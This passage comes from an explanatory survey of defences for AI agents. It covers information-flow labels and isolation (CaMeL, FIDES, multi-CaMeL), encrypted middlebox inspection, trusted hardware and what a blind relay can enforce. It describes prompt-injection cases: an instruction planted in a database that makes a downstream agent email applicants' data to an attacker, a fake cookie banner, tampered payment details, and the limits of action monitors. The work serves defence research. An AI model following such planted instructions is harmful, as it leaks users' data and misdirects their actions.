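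Garby and colleagues wrote a small programming language for agents, LLMbda, and proved a form of noninterference for every program in it. The proof assistant Lean checked the proof. A model's output is random, so the theorem compares probabilities. It allows two runs with different secrets to look different only to the extent that some runs never finish. If `Δ` is the statistical distance between what an observer sees in the two cases, and `d₁` and `d₂` are the probabilities of not finishing, then

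`Δ ≤ (d₁ + d₂) / 2`

If 2% of runs fail to finish in each case, the probability of any visible outcome differs by at most two percentage points.

### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo, a benchmark from 2024, has 97 user tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, travel booking, banking and the messaging service Slack. Testers pair the tasks with attacks that plant instructions in tool results. In May 2025, Costa and colleagues reported these results for GPT-4o. The last four columns give the share of tasks completed without an attack.

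| Agent | Successful attacks | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with policy checks | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES without policy checks | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES with policy checks | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The policy checks stopped the attacks that hiding text had not stopped. Under those checks, hiding text let the agent complete more tasks in every setting except travel. Most of the travel tools were available even in an untrusted conversation, so hiding text helped little there, and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With OpenAI's reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

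The zeros show only that enforcement works when the labels are right, because Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company does not know in advance which fields attackers will use.

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks in 2026, three times per task. With GPT-5.2 and no policy checks, it completed 32 of 48 runs, and one of the 240 attacks that ran to completion succeeded. With the checks on, no attack succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 18 of 48 runs. These results may understate the value of the checks. In about two-thirds of the pairs of task and attack (97 of 144), the attack needs a tool that the user's task would never call, so a fixed plan usually defeats it without any labels. An attacker who knew about the plan would concentrate on altering values, as in the tampered email, and the policies would matter more.

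An agent written in LLMbda did better, completing 36 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2 while enforcing its labels throughout. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. The agent's completion rate depends partly on endorsement, which relabels a particular untrusted value as trusted. Its planner writes the endorsements into the program before reading any outside data. When Garby and colleagues removed endorsement, the agent completed five or six fewer of its 48 runs on each of the two models they tested.

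*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) returns to capabilities in Hardy's sense. Its agent writes programs in the language Scala, and the compiler rejects any program that uses a capability it should not have. Secret data arrives in a wrapper. The program may transform the data inside, but only with functions that hold no capabilities and so cannot write a file or contact the network. Unlike CaMeL and FIDES, the system treats the planner as a possible attacker. According to Garby and colleagues, it resisted all but one of 1,926 attacks on AgentDojo, and the benchmark wrongly counted the exception as a successful attack because the agent had quoted a hotel review word for word.

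All of these systems run more slowly and complete fewer tasks. CaMeL's model writes programs, which are longer than ordinary tool calls, and *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower on AgentDojo than filters or defensive prompts. In FIDES, each question to the quarantined model adds a model call.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that such comparisons leave out the main benefit. An ordinary agent is safe only if a person approves every consequential action, whereas an agent with labels needs approval only when an action fails a policy check. With the model o3-mini, an ordinary agent needed about 48 approvals for the AgentDojo tasks it completed, and FIDES needed about 19. Their system, Prudentia, gives the planner the labels and policies so that it can take them into account. It completed 59% of tasks without any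 approvals, compared with 50% for FIDES and 24% for the ordinary agent.

Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of data. If an email contains a to-do list of ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions. This saves effort, but the endorsement would also cover an eleventh item hidden by an attacker. Kolluri and colleagues assume the user would catch such an attack and leave the design of the approval screen to future work.

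### Agents that hand work to other agents

CaMeL protects a single agent, but the protection can fail when one agent instructs another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL without additional policies. The user asked the system to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent read the applicant database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the data to an outside address. A coordinating agent had the result summarized and included the summary in its request to the messaging agent.

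Neither of the first two planners saw the planted text, but the third agent treated the whole request as coming from its user. Its planner read the instruction in the summary and added a step that emailed the applicants' data to the attacker. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering", because untrusted data becomes trusted by passing from one agent to the next. They prove that any system of two or more agents is vulnerable to this if agents can pass tool results on in their requests and the system has a tool with untrusted output, even when each agent is secure by itself.

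The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into an instruction that the receiving planner can read and a set of named variables whose contents it cannot see. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output and preserves the labels on variables passed between agents.

The evaluation used 949 attacks against each of five models on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded with no defence, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of multi-step professional tasks, running CaMeL in each agent lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points. For the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5, the corresponding drops were 13.4 points and another 0.85 points.

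Critics of isolation get their best evidence from the same test. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks with no defence, and only 1.5% succeeded against Fable 5. If models can learn to ignore injected instructions, a design that loses 13 points is hard to justify. Peters-Gill and colleagues reply that the benchmark's attacks are fixed, and that in large tests, attackers who adapted to their target succeeded against every leading model. A user whose agent summarizes public web pages might reasonably rely on the model's own resistance, but a bank whose agent makes payments has more reason to accept the 13-point loss in exchange for a guarantee.

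Codex would need considerable changes to follow multi-CaMeL's rule, because any task that a parent agent writes after reading tool results would count as untrusted, even if it is encrypted. However, if OpenAI's servers attached a reliable label outside the encryption, the harness could restrict what a subagent does with an untrusted task without reading the text.

### False content and open-ended plans

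Isolation keeps an attacker from adding steps to a plan, but false information can still lead the agent to do the wrong thing. Costa and colleagues describe an email containing an instruction for the quarantined model to produce an empty summary. The assistant then carries out its plan correctly and sends the user's colleague nothing useful. Both successful attacks on the LLMbda agent involved a task in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes, and the attacker replaced the payment details. The user had told the agent to trust the file, so no label could separate the attack from the task. A stricter policy could require every payment detail to come from a trusted source, but then the agent could not use the file to make the payment at all.

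The danger is greater for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to such agents by having the planner write out many possible branches in advance. A quarantined model looks at the screen and answers questions such as whether a cookie banner is visible, and the answer selects a branch. When the researchers disguised an advertisement as a cookie banner, the agent followed its approved plan for closing banners and clicked on the advertisement, which led to the attacker's site. Policies are little help here because they cannot determine the consequences of an action like `click(x, y)` from the action itself. The available defences, such as asking another model to check the screen, are again probabilistic.

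Some tasks are also hard to plan in advance. If a user asks an agent to do whatever is due today on a to-do list, the steps depend on what is on the list. Costa and colleagues classified the AgentDojo tasks by whether the right sequence of actions depends on what the tools return. The sequence depended on tool results in 5% of workspace tasks and 10% of travel tasks, but in about 43% of the banking and Slack tasks.

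A planner can try to cover every possibility, but the programs become long. Foerster and colleagues' programs averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five tool calls and four branches for CaMeL's on AgentDojo. The resulting agent kept at most 57% of the performance that leading models achieve without isolation. A flexible program can also undo the protection that isolation provides. For a banking task that said to follow the instructions in a file precisely, CaMeL's planner wrote a loop that read each instruction and called the matching tool. Anyone who controlled the file could then direct the agent's actions, even though the planner had never seen the text. Only the policy checks could have stopped that attack.

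### Spreading labels and the work of writing policies

Because labels become stricter whenever data is combined, a long session can end with almost nothing permitted. In the FIDES test, for example, the ordinary agent's completion rate on the Slack tasks fell from 93% to 20% once it had to obey the policies. Hiding text in variables slows the spread of strict labels, and endorsement relaxes the labels on chosen values, but each endorsement could also give an attacker a way in.

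Somebody also has to assign the labels and write the policies. Willison, who has two decades of experience in application security, wrote that he was "deeply nervous" about any system that expects ordinary users to think about security policies. Software can infer some labels. For example, FIDES treats an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers, though the sender may have shared the contents more widely. But a company's old files often have no reliable record of who wrote them or who may see them.

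The work is easier for an agent with a narrow job. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* (2025) applies similar designs to ten kinds of application, from simple operating-system assistants to software engineering agents. An agent that only books meetings has a few tools, and its owner can decide in advance who may receive an invitation. The owner of a general assistant that handles email, files and payments would have to make such decisions for every tool and revisit them whenever somebody adds another.

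## The case for checking hidden content with cryptography and secure hardware

Information-flow labels let software restrict a message by its origin and permitted readers, but they don't describe its content. Some cryptographers and hardware designers argue that a relay can also enforce rules about content without seeing the text, which would let a network's owner check messages while senders keep the benefit of encryption. Working prototypes exist for simple rules. Their use for AI agents depends largely on whether anyone can state the rule that an agent needs.

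### Matching encrypted keywords

Much network inspection consists of searching for known strings, such as a phrase that appears in a particular attack. Sherry, Lan and colleagues (2015), in *BlindBox*, showed that a middlebox can do this on encrypted traffic. Their system works as follows:

1. **Keys.** The sender and receiver set up an ordinary TLS connection and derive an extra key `k` from it. The middlebox never gets `k`.
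2. **Encrypted rules.** A rule maker, such as a security company, gives the middlebox a list of signed keywords. For each keyword `r`, the middlebox needs `AES_k(r)`, which is `r` encrypted with `k` under the standard cipher AES. The endpoints send it a garbled circuit, a scrambled program that performs this encryption once without revealing `k`. A companion technique, oblivious transfer, lets the middlebox use its keyword as input without showing it to the endpoints. The program rejects keywords that lack the rule maker's signature.
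3. **Encrypted text.** The sender cuts the text into overlapping pieces of eight bytes, so "delete file" becomes "delete f", "elete fi" and so on. It turns each piece `t` into a five-byte code by encrypting a number called a salt, with `AES_k(t)` as the key. It sends these codes alongside the normal encrypted traffic.
4. **Matching.** The middlebox computes the same code for each of its keywords and looks for equal values. The salt changes whenever a piece repeats, so the middlebox cannot tell that an unlisted word has occurred twice.
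5. **Check on arrival.** The receiver decrypts the text, recomputes the codes and compares them with those the middlebox forwarded. Without this step, a dishonest sender could attach harmless codes to a harmful message.

The middlebox can detect which keywords occur and where, and can count the pieces, but it gets almost no information about the rest of the text. Exact matching is enough for parental filters and for the watermarks that companies put in confidential documents. It is less useful for detecting intrusions, because keywords with positions could express only 29% to 67% of the rules in four intrusion-detection sets. The other rules need more flexible patterns or scripts. For those, BlindBox has a second mode in which a keyword match reveals the session key, and the middlebox then decrypts the whole connection. This mode preserves less privacy the more often innocent traffic contains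 the keywords.

The system is slow to open a connection because every keyword needs its own garbled circuit. Ten keywords took 0.65 seconds, and a typical set of 3,000 intrusion rules, with nearly 10,000 keywords, took 97 seconds. A decade later, *PrivBox* (Wu, Ning and colleagues, 2025) proposed another way to generate the encrypted rules. The codes also use extra bandwidth. Across 50 popular websites, the median page needed 2.5 to 4 times as many bytes, depending on how the sender split the text. Once a connection was open, however, the middlebox kept up with an ordinary intrusion detector.

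BlindBox requires at least one honest endpoint. Two dishonest endpoints could agree on their own key and encrypt the message a second time, and the codes would then match nothing. The endpoints also have to trust the rule maker, which could work with the middlebox to search their traffic for any word.

Codex's delegated tasks don't meet the first requirement, because OpenAI's servers are at both ends and no independent party would perform the check on arrival. A customer's harness could search the codes for the name of a protected file, but the customer would have to trust OpenAI to compute the codes correctly.

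### Proving that a message obeys a rule

In *Zero-Knowledge Middleboxes*, Grubbs, Arun and colleagues moved the inspection to the sender, which checks its own message, encrypts it and attaches a zero-knowledge proof. The proof is a string that lets the relay verify that the message obeys the policy but reveals nothing else about it. The scheme works without changing the server at the other end or notifying it of the proof.

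Their main example is a network that has to block certain websites, as US schools must block adult content. Before a browser opens a site, it asks a server called a DNS resolver for the site's numerical address. Networks have long filtered these lookups, but browsers can now encrypt them and send them to an outside resolver. With a zero-knowledge middlebox, a pupil's laptop would proceed like this:

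1. **Policy.** On joining the network, the laptop downloads the blocklist and arranges it in order in a Merkle tree. The tree hashes the entries in pairs, then hashes the resulting hashes in pairs, until a single hash remains. This root commits the network to the list, because changing any entry would change the root.
2. **Commitment.** The laptop opens a TLS 1.3 connection to the resolver and obtains a session key `K`. It sends the middlebox the hash `h = H(K)`, with a proof that `K` is the key that belongs to the handshake the middlebox has just observed.
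3. **Proof.** The laptop encrypts its lookup as `C`. It then proves that it knows a key `K` for which `H(K) = h`, that decrypting `C` with `K` gives a lookup for some domain `D`, and that `D` is not on the blocklist. To prove the last part, it uses two neighbouring entries. If `bets.example` and `casino.example` are next to each other in the ordered list, then `books.example` cannot be on it.
4. **Verification.** The middlebox checks the proof against `h`, `C` and the root. If the proof is valid, it forwards the lookup, and otherwise it drops it.

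The commitment is needed because, with the ciphers TLS 1.3 uses, someone can construct a ciphertext that decrypts to different messages under different keys. Without the commitment, a dishonest laptop could prove that one message was harmless while the resolver read another. Tying `K` to the handshake leaves only one possible message.

The laptop's part, run on an eight-core cloud machine, took about 14 seconds when the connection opened and 3.1 seconds for each lookup. The middlebox checked each 128-byte proof in less than 5 milliseconds. Grubbs and colleagues did not build the full system, so these figures cover only the proofs. Arranging their blocklist of two million domains in a tree took nearly two hours, probably because that code was unoptimised. In APNIC's *Unpacking zero-knowledge middleboxes* (2022), Paul Grubbs described the method as not yet fully practical but "surprisingly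 close".

*Zombie*, the successor system by Zhang, DeStefano and colleagues, is faster because the part of the proof that takes the most computation does not depend on the message and can be done in advance. TLS can encrypt by combining the text with a stream of random-looking bytes, and the client can generate that stream, and prove that it is correct, while the connection is idle. The delay for each lookup fell below 300 milliseconds. It can fall to zero if the middlebox forwards traffic at once and checks the proofs afterwards. This is reasonable for a school, which can disconnect a laptop that fails a check, but a subagent might have deleted a file before its proof is checked.

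Capacity is still a problem. Zombie's middlebox handled only 380 small packets a second even when it checked proofs in batches, which is far too slow for a busy network to require a proof for every packet.

The middlebox learns that each lookup complies, along with whatever its size and timing already reveal. It does not need to trust the laptop, but in the original design it must trust whoever generated the proof system's public parameters. A dishonest generator could forge proofs, though not read anyone's traffic. Generating Zombie's parameters requires only a source of public randomness.

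A proof covers only the layer of the message it describes. A pupil could still reach a blocked site through a VPN or hide a forbidden message under a second layer of encryption. Grubbs and colleagues deliberately accept this limit because they think blocking every way around a filter would amount to censorship. A company that wants to contain a hijacked agent may be less willing to accept it.

For agents, the most promising use is probably answering a narrow question about a hidden message. Zombie supports rules based on text patterns, including those companies use to prevent leaks of confidential data. It takes 1 to 2 milliseconds per byte, or one to two seconds for a task of 1,000 characters. OpenAI could in principle commit to its encryption key and prove that a delegated task contains no text in the format of a customer's passwords. After the loss of `customers.csv`, OpenAI could prove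 whether the task had named that file without disclosing the rest of the task.

### Inspectors in sealed processors

Secure hardware can run much more complicated checks. A trusted execution environment (TEE) is a part of a computer that the processor isolates from everything else on the machine, including the operating system and its administrators. According to Schneier on Security's *New Attacks Against Secure Enclaves*, TEEs "decouple who runs the chip" from who secures it. The cloud company runs the chip, and the manufacturer secures it.

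Remote attestation is meant to show users what software a TEE is running before they send it data. *Private AI clouds are the future of inference* describes the process. The hardware hashes the firmware, the operating system's kernel and the program, then signs the hash, which is called the measurement. The user's device checks the signature and compares the measurement with the one expected for the approved software. If they match, the device sends its data encrypted to the TEE.

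An inspector could run this way in the middle of a network. The endpoints would give it their session keys, and it would decrypt each message, apply the policy and send the relay only its decision on whether to forward the message. Grubbs and colleagues cite several such designs, including EndBox, which puts the inspector in a TEE on the user's own computer. A TEE runs ordinary programs, so the policy could be a large classifier. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that trusted hardware promises good performance but avoid it because researchers have broken it so often.

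The largest test of the idea so far is in messaging, where Meta's Private Processing lets WhatsApp users have an AI model summarise their messages on Meta's servers. According to *The Day the Provider Stopped Reading Your Chats* (2026), the system runs on AMD and Nvidia processors and is designed to keep the text from Meta's own administrators. Meta has also announced Side Chat, which will let people consult its AI within an existing conversation. Pogorelec (2026) reports in *Meta locks itself out of user data on its AI glasses* that Meta extended the system to its AI glasses in September 2026. These services process messages for users and do not police them, but an inspector in a TEE would depend on the same hardware and attestation.

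### What an audit of WhatsApp's system found

Before the launch, Meta had a security company examine Private Processing. Trail of Bits' *What we learned about TEE security from auditing WhatsApp's Private Inference* (2026) reports 28 problems, eight of them severe. Several would have let an attacker read messages while the attestation still appeared valid:

- **Settings loaded too late.** The system read some configuration files after the hardware had taken the measurement. A malicious employee could have used them to load extra code that copied every message, and the measurement would not have changed.
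- **Fake devices.** The measurement left out the tables that tell an operating system what hardware it has. The software that manages the virtual machine could have invented a device with access to protected memory.
- **Unverified patch level.** The user's app accepted the firmware's own statement of which security updates it had. Old firmware with known flaws could have lied.
- **Reusable reports.** An attestation report had no link to a particular connection. Somebody who broke into one TEE once could have kept its report and keys, and used them to impersonate the service indefinitely.

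Meta fully fixed 16 of the problems before launch and partly fixed four. It left eight minor ones unfixed and gave its reasons for each. Trail of Bits concluded that TEEs can support private AI features if developers get hundreds of details right, and that the faults lay in the implementation rather than the idea.

Later work led by Muhammad Usama Sardar of TU Dresden, described in SC Media's *Confidential computing’s remote attestation protocol may have fundamental flaw* (2026), found a weakness in attested TLS, which combines attestation with an encrypted connection. Attestation establishes what software is running but not which machine is running it. An attacker can therefore let a client verify a genuine server and divert the connection to a compromised machine, which receives the data. Sardar's team tested seven ways of binding the attestation to the connection, and none prevented the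 attack. The weakness affects Meta's Private Processing, among other systems. The attacker still needs a compromised machine, but because the flaw is in the protocol, careful programming by one company may not remove it.

Secure hardware is also vulnerable to physical attacks. According to *TEEs Are The Worst They'll Ever Be*, two recent attacks, WireTap and Battering RAM, need physical access to the computer, and manufacturers exclude such attacks from their security promises. That exclusion may be acceptable to a customer worried about remote hackers, but it is harder to accept when the party to be kept out owns the building. An article from the ACLU, a US civil liberties group, makes this objection to AI in encrypted messaging. *AI and Secure Messaging Don't Mix*, a post by the same writer, calls the foundations "shaky", especially against a company as powerful as Meta.

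The same problem would affect an inspector for Codex. If it ran on the customer's computer, the customer could try to break it open and read OpenAI's hidden tasks. If it ran in OpenAI's data centre, the customer would rely on hardware in OpenAI's possession to check OpenAI's messages. A third company could host it, but both sides would then have to trust that company.

### The dispute over private AI in messaging apps

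The EFF does not think TEEs have resolved the conflict between secure messaging and AI. In *Secure Messaging and AI Remain In Conflict Despite the Promise of TEEs*, Portnoy and Klosowski (2026) worry less about AI features that run entirely on a phone than about those that need more computing power and so send text to a company's server. The EFF has also demanded that AI features in messaging apps not leak text automatically, that users be able to switch them off, and that AI built into a device read encrypted conversations only if the user opts in.

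Meta set out its own view before the EFF's September post. Its chief executive, Mark Zuckerberg, has likened the privacy of Incognito Chat, a private mode for talking to Meta's AI, to that of end-to-end encryption, according to *Meta AI’s Incognito Chat*. The comparison describes Meta's aim fairly, since the company is supposed to be unable to read the text in both cases, but it overstates the similarity. With a TEE, the company's servers hold the readable message, and its secrecy depends on the chip, the attestation and the software around them.

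de Alfaro, Fábrega and colleagues, in *AI Assistants*, take a position between the two. They consider TEEs an improvement on ordinary processing of readable text, but no substitute for end-to-end encryption. Computing directly on encrypted data would avoid the need for trusted hardware, but they say it is still impractical for AI.

Locking the company out also weakens safety. *Meta AI's Incognito Chat* points out that human reviewers can no longer easily examine conversations for signs of danger. An automated monitor inside the TEE could do part of that job. *On TEEs for Privacy-Preserving Monitoring in AI Governance*, from MIRI, a research institute concerned with catastrophic risks from AI, discusses this kind of monitoring and argues that privacy and the prevention of misuse need not exclude each other. It also warns that TEEs don't solve every problem of trust, since they can leak information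 through side channels such as timing and require trust in the manufacturer.

### Turning "no harmful instruction" into a rule

All of these methods need a rule that a program can apply, such as "the domain is not on this list." Two people who apply that rule will always agree. "The message contains no harmful instruction" doesn't qualify, because the same words can be harmful in one message and proper in another, like the file name given to Hardy's compiler. The program would need to know at least what the user had asked for and what the recipient could do, and even then people might disagree about the answer.

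A list of forbidden phrases is easy to check but misses anything an attacker has reworded. A strict format, like the restricted answers in FIDES, works better. For example, a task might have to consist of one verb from a fixed list and one file name from a folder the user has chosen. A sender can prove in zero knowledge that a hidden task has this format, but not that it names the right file. Most tasks people give agents do not fit such a format.

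The remaining option is to use a classifier in place of the definition. The rule becomes `f(m) = safe`, where `m` is the hidden message and `f` is a model with specified weights. A program can check this rule exactly, but a proof shows only that this classifier labeled this message safe. The proof is still valid when the classifier is wrong, so a relay should not treat "proved safe" as stronger evidence of safety than "classified as safe".

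The proof must also identify the classifier, because otherwise a sender could use a model that labels everything safe. The usual way to do this is to publish a commitment to the weights, such as a hash, and prove that the weights used match it. If the weights themselves are public, anyone can evaluate the model, but an attacker can also privately test different wordings until one passes. Keeping the weights secret makes this harder, and BlindBox hides its keywords from the endpoints for much the same reason. However, the relay must then rely on someone else's assurance that the committed model works well.

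### The cost of proving a classifier's answer

Zhang and colleagues list a neural network's output among the things a zero-knowledge proof can establish, but in practice the size of the network makes this difficult. The proof systems behind these middleboxes first turn a program into a long list of equations, and proving time grows at least in proportion to the number of equations. Comparing two numbers takes many more equations than multiplying them, and many neural networks make a comparison at every artificial neuron to decide whether it should be active.

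Figures from Grubbs and colleagues allow a rough estimate of how long it would take to prove a language classifier's answer. Their largest case study, a check that traffic uses the web's HTTP protocol, involved about 1.5 million multiplications and took 21 seconds to prove, or roughly 72,000 multiplications a second. A typical language classifier performs about one multiplication per weight for each token it reads. With 100 million weights, which is small by current standards, it would need 50 billion multiplications for a 500-token web page, and the proof would take about eight days at the same speed. To prove the answer for a 100-token message in ten seconds, the classifier could have only about 7,000 weights, too few to understand much language.

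These numbers rule out using the 2022 method directly, but proof systems designed for neural networks can handle much larger models. Most of a network's computation is multiplying large tables of numbers, and these systems rely on the fact that checking such a multiplication takes far less work than repeating it. For a relay, the relevant limit is how long a message can wait. An investigator who wants to know what a classifier answered last week can wait hours for a proof, but an agent that delegates dozens of tasks in a session may not be able to wait a minute for each.

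A TEE avoids the wait by running the classifier normally and attesting to which model it ran. The relay gets the same answer from the classifier as it would with a zero-knowledge proof, but it relies on the chip's manufacturer and whoever physically controls the machine, rather than only on mathematics and correct software.

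## What a relay can establish without reading a message

A relay with no proof about a hidden message, and no trusted hardware to examine it, can judge the message only by its envelope. Supporters of inspection and supporters of encryption disagree about how adequate this is. The envelope is useful evidence when harmful messages look different from the outside, as spam often does, but otherwise no rule based on envelopes can separate them from the rest.

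### Messages with the same envelope

Suppose a relay decides whether to block a message using only the message's envelope `e` and the history `h` of earlier envelopes, perhaps with some randomness. Its rule is then a function `b(e, h)` that gives the probability of blocking. If a harmful message and a harmless one have the same envelope and history, the relay blocks both with the same probability. Among such messages, whatever the rule, the share of harmful ones it blocks (its detection rate) equals, on average, the share of harmless ones it blocks (its false-alarm rate).

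Here is what that means for 1,000 such messages, of which 10 are harmful. The figures for random blocking are averages.

| Relay's rule | Harmful messages blocked | Harmful messages passed | Harmless messages blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Pass everything | 0 | 10 | 0 |
| Block one in ten at random | 1 | 9 | 99 |
| Block half at random | 5 | 5 | 495 |
| Block everything | 10 | 0 | 990 |

Whatever rule the relay uses to block messages, about one in 100 of the messages it blocks is harmful, the same proportion as in the traffic as a whole. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, proves a more general result for software that checks an agent's actions before they run. The available information and the tolerated rate of missed violations determine a minimum false-alarm rate, and no combination of models using the same information can get below it. Additional information can lower that minimum,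 but doesn't always.

Usually the envelopes of harmful and harmless messages differ a little. If 60% of harmful messages and 20% of harmless ones are longer than 2,000 bytes, a relay that blocks long messages stops 6 of the 10 harmful ones and 198 of the 990 harmless ones. In general,

`detection rate − false-alarm rate ≤ Δ`

where `Δ` is the statistical distance between the envelopes of the two groups. It is 0.4 in this example if length is the only difference, and 0 when the envelopes are distributed identically.

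An attacker who knows the rule can shorten the message. Spammers have more trouble adapting because they need to reach many people, which a relay can see from the envelope.

The information a relay lacks may be the source of an instruction rather than its text. Ray built 123 pairs of cases with identical actions and instructions, which differed only in whether the instruction came from the user or from a tool's output. A judge that sees only the action can do no better than chance on these pairs. When Ray added the source, a model with 7 billion parameters rated the unauthorised case as riskier about 97% of the time, counting ties as half. A model with 3 billion parameters scored 56%, and one with half a billion stayed at chance. A reliable source label outside the encryption could therefore help a relay that cannot read the message, provided that whatever reads the label can use it.

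The calculation with 1,000 messages also assumes that blocking one message has no effect on the next, but an agent may respond to a refusal by trying something else. Ray ran 389 tasks with and without a program that checked each proposed action. For the stricter of two such programs, 34 attacks succeeded only when it was off, and five succeeded only when it was on. For the more lenient program, the figures were 29 and 22. Error rates measured on recorded traffic may therefore be a poor guide to how much harm a relay prevents in use.

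### Rules that an observer can enforce

A relay that cannot recognise harmful messages can still enforce other rules. Fred Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), worked out which rules are within reach of a mechanism that watches a program's steps and stops the program when it is about to break one. Firewalls and an operating system's access checks are mechanisms of this kind. Such a rule has to meet three conditions:

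- It judges each run of the program by itself, without comparing it with other runs.
- Once a run has broken the rule, nothing the program does later can make up for it.
- Every violation becomes apparent after a finite number of steps.

Rules that meet these conditions are called safety properties, and they require that some particular bad thing never happens. Access control qualifies because a violation is an attempt at a forbidden operation. A guarantee that a program will eventually get a reply does not, because the reply might still come no matter how long the program has waited. A 30-second deadline meets all three conditions, but the mechanism can't enforce it because it can't stop time from passing.

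Schneider represents enforceable rules as state machines. For a rule that forbids sending messages after reading a file, the machine starts in a state called "no file read", in which the program may send. Reading a file moves it to the state "file read", which has no transition for sending. If the program then tries to send a message, the mechanism stops it.

Basin et al. (2012) summarise one of Schneider's requirements as follows: the sequence of actions must be enough to determine whether the program has complied. A blind relay has less than that sequence. Write `env(s)` for the envelopes it observes during a run `s`, and `ok(s)` for whether the run obeys the rule. The relay can enforce the rule exactly only if

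`env(s) = env(s′) ⇒ ok(s) = ok(s′)`

The same-envelope argument also applies to whole sessions. If a forbidden session and a permitted session produce the same envelopes, the relay has to stop both or neither.

Three rules that Ray uses for an email and payments assistant show how much a relay loses:

- **Send nothing after the user revokes access.** A blind relay can enforce this, because it observes the revocation and every later attempt to send.
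- **Never transfer more than a set amount to one recipient in a day.** The relay needs each amount, so the sender would have to put it outside the encryption, and the relay would have to trust that it matched the amount inside.
- **Never email personal data to an unapproved recipient.** The rule depends on the text, and even a relay that could read it would need a fallible judge to decide what counts as personal data.

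For the last rule, a blind relay could instead enforce a stricter one that blocks all email to unapproved recipients. Schneider notes that enforcing a stricter rule always enforces the original too, but it also stops runs that did nothing wrong, and in the extreme case it stops every run.

Writing the rules correctly is a separate problem. *Tether* (2026) describes a system that enforces policies on agents, and the policy in its experiments has 24 rules and lists of exceptions. The system checks such a policy by having a language model write a proof that certain guarantees hold for sessions of any length, which Lean then verifies. The proof covers the rules but not the description of events that the rules depend on. Schneider points out that a program may have many ways to send a message, some obscure, and that a rule against sending has to include them all.

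### What reading cannot detect either

Noninterference fails Schneider's first condition because it compares runs with different secrets. This also limits layers that can read messages. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a scheduling assistant that may reveal when its user is free, but not why the user is busy at other times. The assistant offers slot 10 in a run where a busy slot is an ordinary meeting, and slot 11 in a run where the same busy slot is a confidential interview. Either offer is acceptable by itself, and only a comparison of the two runs shows that the offer depended on the reason.

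A harmless assistant might also have offered slot 11, so a monitor that checks single runs will either raise a false alarm on the harmless assistant or miss the leaking one. Pandey and colleagues tested nine language models as monitors that judged one action at a time. Eight never blocked the leaking runs, and the ninth blocked them in 3 of 30 trials. Given both runs together, eight of the nine recognised the leak every time.

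The same test contains good evidence for inspecting messages. All nine models blocked an open attempt to forward data to an outsider in every trial, which a blind relay could do only if the recipient's address revealed the attempt. Pandey and colleagues divide authorisation failures into eight classes. A monitor that treats the agent as a black box detects none of them, while the best monitor of single runs covers seven, one of them with some false alarms. How quickly coverage grows between these two monitors depends on how the classes are divided, but the overall difference is large.

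Some of that coverage comes from keeping a running total. In another experiment, an assistant based on the model Qwen3-30B disclosed more of a calendar than its user had agreed to in 22 of 60 runs, although each step was allowed on its own. A guard that added up the disclosures and refused any beyond the agreed amount prevented all of these failures and blocked none of the harmless runs. A blind relay can also keep totals, but only of things it can count without reading the messages, such as messages, bytes and recipients.

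### Guarantees and their assumptions

Any guarantee from a relay depends on conditions that Schneider sets out for enforcement in general: the mechanism must observe every relevant step and be able to stop the program, and the program must be unable to tamper with it. An agent that can reach the recipient by another route can bypass every rule the relay applies. The table lists the additional assumptions for each kind of claim.

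| Claim about | What a blind relay can establish | Assumption, or reason for failure |
|---|---|---|
| Destination | The message goes only to an approved address | The recipient does not pass it on |
| Sender | The holder of a particular key signed the message | Nobody has stolen the key, and the relay can check the signature without decrypting |
| Integrity | Nobody has changed the ciphertext since the sender signed it | The relay has the sender's genuine public key |
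| Order | No earlier message is missing, and none arrives twice | The signature covers a sequence number, and the relay remembers the last one |
| Rate | The sender stays below a set number of messages per hour | The sender has no second account |
| Size | The message stays below a set number of bytes | The recipient does not unpack a compressed payload into something far larger |
| Recipient's authority | The recipient can take only certain actions | Software outside the recipient enforces the limit |
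| Truth | Nothing | A false statement can have the same envelope as a true one |
| Intent | Nothing | Honest and malicious senders can produce the same envelope |
| Absence of instructions | Nothing | A planted instruction can replace other text of the same length |
| Absence of secrets | At most, that the message is too short to contain a large file | A password fits in almost any message |

The guarantees in the upper rows could all hold for the hidden task that led to the loss of `customers.csv`. The parent agent did send the task to the right subagent, in the right order and at an ordinary length. But it may have copied the instruction from a malicious web page, and a signature would not reveal this because it identifies only the agent that wrote the message.

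### Limiting what the recipient can do

Of the properties in the table, only the recipient's authority directly limits harm from a message that nobody can read. An authority limit is the set of actions a recipient is able to take, whatever a message tells it to do. Let `A` be the set of all sequences of actions within that limit, and `H(a)` the harm that a sequence `a` would cause. Whatever message `m` leads the recipient to do must be in `A`, so

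`harm caused by m ≤ the largest H(a) for any a in A`

The right-hand side does not depend on `m`, so the bound holds for every payload, including encrypted messages and kinds of attack that nobody has invented yet. The bound also does not require an estimate of how many messages are harmful.

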